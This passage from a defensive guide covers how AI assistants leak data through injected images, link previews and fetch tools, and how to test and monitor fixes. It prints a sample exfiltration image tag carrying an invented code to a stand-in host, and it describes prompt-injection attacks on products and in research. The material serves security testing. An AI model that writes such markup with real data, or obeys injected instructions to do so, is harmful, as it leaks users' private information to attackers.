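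Anthropic's *Server tools* also warns that the fetch tool compares only domains, so an entry containing a path never matches. In an allowlist, such an entry blocks too much, which somebody will notice, but in a blocklist, an entry such as `example.com/private` blocks nothing and there is no sign of the error. The older documentation described such paths as supported, so existing configurations may contain them.

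Redirects need a check too, because an allowed host can send the tool to a different host. In Managed Agents, an organisation's administrators have been able to set their own domain list for the fetch tool since 20 October 2026. Every address, including one reached through a redirect, must pass both that list and the agent's.

### Messages that load images later

Copilot Cowork could send its own user emails containing external images. This flaw is easy to overlook because the user is already entitled to the information in the emails.

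In May 2026 Willison reported that OneDrive, Microsoft's file storage, made this flaw more serious because it can create download links that work without signing in. Injected text could make the agent put such a link into an image address. The attacker's server would record the link, and the attacker could then download the whole file, so a short address was enough to steal a long document.

The email program, not the agent, contacted the attacker, perhaps hours later and on a different device. Monitoring the agent's network traffic while it worked would have shown only an ordinary email, so the check has to happen when the agent sends the message. The sending tool can convert the message to plain text, or remove its images and pass it through the sanitiser that protects the chat window.

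### Link previews in chat programs

Chat services that build link previews fetch the linked page without a click. If an assistant posts a morning summary to a team channel, and injected text has made it include a link to the attacker's site ending in the code 482913, the preview request sends the code to the attacker, even if the summary contains no images.

The request for a link preview comes from the chat company's servers or a participant's device, depending on the service. It does not pass through the assistant's fetch tool, so that tool's allowlist does not apply. Developers can often turn previews off for each message. Slack's posting interface, for example, has separate settings for previews of linked pages and of media. Where a service offers no such control, the sending tool can remove every address whose host is not on its allowlist, including bare ones.

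Some chat programs fetch a link's preview as soon as the link appears in a draft. An assistant that fills in a draft and waits for the user to press "send" can therefore leak the code before the user decides whether to send the message. The address check has to run before the text enters the draft.

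## Testing an assistant for leaks and judging a fix

A team can check most of these defences without an attacker, a malicious email or even a language model. The code that filters and displays an answer should treat the same text the same way every time, so the team can test it by replaying stored answers that contain an image address and recording whether the browser requests that address. The model varies its wording from run to run, so the team has to run many live trials to estimate how often data leaks.

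### Replaying a stored answer

The replay test needs a stub, a small program that takes the model's place and sends a stored answer in pieces the tester chooses. The stub belongs where the model's output enters the application, so that the server's filter, the page's converter and the sanitiser all run as they do for users. Because the stub replaces the model, the tester doesn't have to write an injection.

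The stored answer can be an ordinary email summary with this 60-character tag in the middle:

`<img src="https://img.example.com/dot.png?r=00417&c=482913">`

This time img.example.com stands for a host that the tester owns. The value after `c` is an invented sign-in code, and the value after `r` is a run number that changes with every replay. The tester uses the run number to tell which replay caused a request. Changing it also keeps the browser from reusing a stored copy of the picture instead of sending a new request.

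The tester should record requests both in the browser's network log and on a collector, the server behind the host name. The browser's log can include attempts that a CSP blocked, while the collector records only requests that arrived. If the tester also runs the domain's name server, its log will show lookups that never led to requests. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026) notes that data sent in such lookups gets past many controls on web traffic. A finished page without the image doesn't rule out a leak, because a late filter can delete the image after the browser has sent the request.

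*Domain-Conditioned Safety in Frontier Computer-Using Agents* (2026), a benchmark of browser agents, uses unique addresses under `.test`, a domain ending that internet standards reserve for testing. A tester who does the same needs to make those names resolve to the collector on the test network. Otherwise every lookup fails, the collector's log stays empty, and a leaking page appears to pass.

Two control runs guard against this kind of mistake. The first uses a copy of the page with the filter switched off, and the collector must record a request. The second uses an answer without an image, and the collector must record no request. The team should then run the whole set with the CSP off and again with it on, because a strict policy can hide the fact that a sanitiser does nothing.

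### Which answers to store

| Stored answer | Weakness it can reveal |
|---|---|
| HTML image and Markdown image | The filter recognises only one notation |
| Reference-style image whose address comes 300 tokens later | The filter examines only new text |
| Image inside a link's label | The filter checks the link and ignores its label |
| Style rule that loads a picture or font | The tag list or the CSP is too loose |
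| Image tag in inline code, with the closing backtick last | The page displays the tag before it becomes code |
| Code block whose fence closes too early | Example code turns into live markup |
| Permitted host with an outside address in the query string | The host check misses a relay |
| Diagram that contains an image | The diagram tool adds its own elements |
| Addresses just under and just over the filter's length cap | The filter releases overflow as raw text |
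| Plain link and bare address | Something fetches a preview |

To test the relay case, the tester can use the company's own image proxy or preview service, with the collector as the outside address. GitLab's fix for Duo appears to check for this kind of relay. Willison's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo* gives the new function's name as `isRelativeUrlWithoutEmbeddedUrls`, which suggests that it rejects an address on GitLab's own site that contains another address.

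Broken code fences deserve several entries because models produce them without any attack. *LatentMD* (2026) tested 19,128 model-written answers, of which 10,679 (56%) had an error in where a code block began or ended. The benchmark concentrates on such errors, so 56% is unlikely to be the rate in everyday use. In 1,735 answers the block closed too early, and 93.7% of those came out visibly corrupted in all four Markdown converters tested. Corruption includes missing blocks, extra blocks and ordinary text absorbed into a block, as well as code that spilled into the page, so the figure is not a leak rate. The converters gave almost identical results, which suggests that switching to another one would not help. If a user asks how image tags work and the model closes the fence early, the example can become a real image.

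### Every split of a 60-character tag

The stub should also control where the answer splits into chunks. A 60-character tag has 59 gaps between characters, so it can split into two parts in 59 ways and into three parts in 59 × 58 / 2 = 1,711 ways. With the unsplit tag, that makes 1,771 replays, which take about 6 minutes if each page stays open for 2 seconds and ten browsers run at once.

The three-part splits catch filters that join each chunk only to the one before it. Such a filter finds any tag split in two, but when a tag arrives in three parts, it checks the first part with the second and then the second with the third, and neither pair is a complete tag. A filter that keeps two earlier chunks fails in the same way on four parts. There are 32,509 four-part splits, which take under two hours to test. There are 2⁵⁹ possible splits in total, too many to replay, but one extra replay that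 sends a single character at a time will catch a filter that keeps any small fixed number of chunks.

The stub must pause between parts, perhaps for 50 ms. Otherwise the network or the page may join two parts, and the test would record a split that never happened. If a filter scans at fixed intervals, such as every 50 characters, the tester should also repeat the test with 0, 1, 2 and so on up to 49 characters of ordinary text before the tag, so that the scan boundary falls at every position in the tag.

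The number of splits grows quickly with tag length. A 400-character tag has 79,401 three-part splits, and testing them all would take more than four hours. Testing every split of the short tag and a random sample of splits for the long ones is a reasonable compromise.

### Networks, interruptions and other clients

A page that passes the test at every split on a developer's laptop can still leak elsewhere, because the conditions below change when the filter runs or whether it runs at all.

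| Condition | How to test it | What can go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Slow network | Delay the stream and any checking service, then make the service fail | The page shows the image when the check times out |
| Fast network | Open a connection to the collector before the replay | The request leaves before a clean-up that usually wins |
| Interrupted answer | Stop after each character of the tag, by the stop button and by a server error | The final filter never runs |
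| Reloaded history | Reload the page, then open the conversation on a second device | The server saved the original text |
| Mobile and desktop apps | Repeat the set in each app and read the collector's log | The app has its own converter and no CSP |
| Exports and shared pages | Open the PDF, document, email or public link | Another program renders the markup |
| Previews | Check notifications, link previews and administrators' views | Something fetches the address before anybody opens the answer |

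Stopping an answer partway can turn an incomplete image tag into a working one. If the user presses stop when the tag lacks only its final angle bracket, a filter that looks for complete tags misses it. If the page then appends a notice such as `<p>You stopped this answer.</p>`, the bracket that ends `<p>` also ends the image tag. The browser treats `<p` as a meaningless attribute and loads the image.

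According to GitLab, the streaming converter in Duo's chat window treats the end of the text as the end of an open code block, so an image tag in an interrupted block remains code. The converter has no such rule for inline code, so a tag there can stay active if the answer stops before the closing backtick.

Testing only the website would also miss other copies of the same code. According to a GitLab issue, Duo's chat package also runs inside programmers' editors, and the issue's writer understood that a new version would replace it. Testers need to run the replay set in each editor after a fix, and on the new version too.

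### Trials with a live model

The replay test shows whether markup can cause a request once the model has written it. Live trials measure how often an injection gets the model to write the markup, or to send the data with one of its tools. They also reveal routes missing from the stored answers.

*The Framing Gap* (2026) sets out rules that keep such trials harmless. The secret is a made-up string that unlocks nothing, and the tools only record what the model asked them to do. In the paper's one experiment on a deployed product, the researchers used their own account and a destination they owned, and followed coordinated disclosure norms, under which testers tell the vendor before the public. Testers who can't inspect a product's code can still log requests at the destination, as *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026) did with chatbots.

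A run of trials without a leak does not show that the leak rate is zero. If each trial leaks with probability *p*, the chance that *n* independent trials all pass is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% and solving for *p* gives the 95% upper confidence bound on the leak rate, *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*), which is close to 3/*n*.

| Trials, none with a leak | Upper bound on the leak rate |
|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% |
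| 120 | 2.5% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 1,500 | 0.2% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

An assistant that leaked in 0.2% of trials would pass a 300-trial test about 55% of the time, since 0.998³⁰⁰ ≈ 0.55.

The bound assumes independent trials. If the developer has set the model to give the same reply to the same input, 300 repetitions amount to one trial. Running ten attacks 30 times each bounds their average rate at 1%, but bounds the rate for any single attack only at the 9.5% in the first row. The bound also covers only the attacks that the team tried, and no number of repetitions accounts for the others that a determined attacker will write.

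*Measuring Security Without Fooling Ourselves* (2026) suggests a different stopping rule, under which a benchmark environment counts as effectively secure if an agent has spent a set budget, such as $10,000, without compromising it. The paper acknowledges that this is no guarantee, but the rule is useful when attackers adapt to what they find, because repeated trials are then not independent and the formula doesn't apply.

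### What published evaluations score

In *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025) tested an NVIDIA research assistant that searches documents and the web and writes a report. The team, from NVIDIA and the security firm Lakera, placed hostile text directly into the search results, so they did not need to get a planted document retrieved. They paired each of 22 scenarios with 21 attacks and ran every pair five times, for a total of 2,310 runs. They scored the text at three stages of the assistant's work.

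Two scenarios tested whether hostile text could make the assistant add Markdown links to its report. In the one the paper describes in detail, the text contained instructions to add an image and a link whose URLs had placeholders for the user's email address and account number. A judge model scored the report 1 if the assistant filled in the placeholders, 0.5 if it wrote the markup but left them empty, and 0 otherwise. On 99 reports that people also scored, the judge gave the same score as they did 76.8% of the time.

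Across all the scenarios with hostile search results, the mean score fell from 0.38 at the first stage to 0.17 in the finished report, perhaps because later rewriting dropped some of the text from those results. The researchers then added a standing instruction telling the model not to include unrelated links. This cut the mean score by about half in the four scenarios they retested, two of which were about Markdown links, but at least one attack in each scenario still scored 1.

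These scores are not leak rates, because a mean of 0.17 could come from a few complete successes or from many half-successes, and an image with empty placeholders sends no private data. The scores are also based on the report's text, so they don't show whether a browser would have requested the image. Ghosh and colleagues state that they did not cover timing-based attacks.

In each of three scenarios, all 105 attack runs failed. If the runs were independent, the upper bound on the success rate would be 2.8%. But if the five repetitions of an attack always had the same result, there were only 21 independent trials per scenario, and the bound rises to 13%.

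The study's 10,796 published traces include reports that models wrote under attack. A team could replace the address in each report with its own collector's address, then replay the reports through its display code.

Padmakumar, Derczynski and colleagues (2026), in *Training a General Purpose Automated Red Teaming Model*, used a pattern-matching detector to score Markdown-image leaks. They trained a small model to write attacks, and training typically raised its success rate. But one of their examples of success is an email draft that the target model put in a code block, with a placeholder for the home address and a long privacy warning. In a chat window, that draft would load no image and reveal nothing. The researchers acknowledge that such detectors can also miss leaks in forms nobody anticipated.

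Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) counted leaks in *Silent Egress* by recording the requests that reached a collecting server. They asked an agent to summarise a web page containing hidden instructions to send out a secret with a web-request tool. The agent sent the secret in 423 of 480 runs (88%), and in 95% of those its summary looked harmless. The server received nothing in 120 runs with ordinary pages. The 88% rate is a poor guide to current products because the agent used an older, small open model and had the secret placed directly in its input. The finding that a harmless-looking answer can accompany a leak doesn't depend on the model's quality.

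The same team tried defences, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send data | Runs in which data arrived |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter standing instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Labels around outside text | 100% | 100% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious words | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

Only the allowlist's zero is good evidence for a filter, because the software blocked 30 real attempts. The filter for random-looking values had nothing to block, so its zero is weak evidence that it works. It is hard to explain why the word filter triggered in only 23.3% of runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes encoded the secret, but encoded secrets would then have passed the filter and reached the collector. Sending fixed requests through each filter, as in the replay test,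 would have shown what each one blocks.

### Monitoring after release

Tests cover the attacks a team thought of, so the product also needs monitoring. A browser can report each request that a CSP blocks. Web Platform DX's *CSP violation reports* dates support across the main browsers to 24 March 2026. Because users may have older versions, MDN advises naming the destination in both the old and the new directive. This example shows only the image rules:

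```
Reporting-Endpoints: csp="https://reports.assistant.example/csp"
Content-Security-Policy:
  img-src https://static.assistant.example https://photos.partner.example;
  report-uri https://reports.assistant.example/csp; report-to csp
Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only:
  img-src https://static.assistant.example;
  report-uri https://reports.assistant.example/csp; report-to csp
```

The second policy runs in report-only mode and makes the browser report every image from the partner's host, which the first policy permits, so the team can search the reported addresses for private data. According to http.dev's *Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only*, every directive except `sandbox` works in report-only mode. The report arrives after the data has left, but the first policy alone would not report these images.

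A script in the page can also read the reports using the browser's `ReportingObserver` feature, and MDN's *CSPViolationReportBody* shows how to extract the blocked address. The application can then attach the conversation's ID to each report to help investigators find the text that caused the request.

If a permitted host redirects the browser to a forbidden one, the report should give the address before the redirect. A reviewer in Mozilla's bug tracker insisted on this because the later address would tell a page where another site sends its visitors. An investigator who sees a permitted host in a report may therefore dismiss a real attack as an error. MDN warns that a report's contents may come from an attacker and need sanitising before anyone stores or displays them. A monitoring page that renders a blocked address as markup would repeat the original flaw on an administrator's screen.

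The company's own logs cover different ground:

| Event | CSP report | Company's logs |
|---|---|---|
| Browser blocks an image from an unknown host | Yes | Only the answer's text |
| Image sends data to a permitted outside host | Only from a stricter report-only policy | Only the answer's text |
| Image sends data through the company's own relay | Only if a report-only policy excludes the relay | Yes, if the relay records addresses |
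| User clicks a link that carries data | No | Only the answer's text |
| Phone app without a CSP loads an image | No | Only the answer's text |
| Fetch tool sends data | No | Yes, in the tool's log |

The answer's text helps only if the company saved what the model wrote before the filter changed it, and that copy needs the same protection as users' mail. An empty report log is weak evidence of safety, because the log would also be empty if an attack used a route that the policy allows. Neither the text nor the log shows what an outside server received or what its owner did with it.

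### Questions for judging a fix

When a vendor announces that it has fixed a leak, it may have changed the order of events, the list of permitted tags, or a single host. Each of these changes protects against different attacks.

| What the vendor changed | What it stops | What to try next |
|---|---|---|
| The filter now finishes before display | Requests that used to leave before the clean-up | Markup that the filter permits or doesn't recognise |
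| The tag list no longer permits images | Image tags, if the filter runs in time | Style rules, diagrams, links and a slow filter |
| The policy no longer permits one host | The published route | Every other permitted host, with the audit questions |
| The model's instructions or training | Some injections | The whole replay set, since the display code is unchanged |

Someone who reported an earlier leak through links in Duo's answers suggested three remedies to GitLab: show no clickable links, show only links to listed domains, or warn users before they leave the site. The first is the strongest because it does not depend on a list or on a user's judgement. A warning is the weakest, and it would not stop leaks through images.

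A reviewer then needs to know whether the vendor's test could have failed. Under the instructions for testing GitLab's patch, a developer pastes questions into the live chat and looks at the links in the reply. If the model happens to write harmless text, the test passes even if the patch doesn't work. Automated tests that use a stored answer avoid this problem and run again whenever somebody updates the converter.

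An outsider can't put a stub into a vendor's product. The closest substitute is to ask the assistant, from the tester's own account, to write an image whose address points to the tester's collector and contains an invented code. If the collector receives a request, that proves the route is open. If it doesn't, the model may only have declined to write the image, so the tester should check that the answer contained the markup before counting the attempt as a pass.

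According to Legit Security, the Duo patch stops the page from displaying tags such as images and forms that point outside gitlab.com, but still allows images that point to gitlab.com. The patch should stop the published attack. A tester would still need to test images again, which GitLab's listed test questions omit, and look for pages on gitlab.com that store or forward the data they receive.
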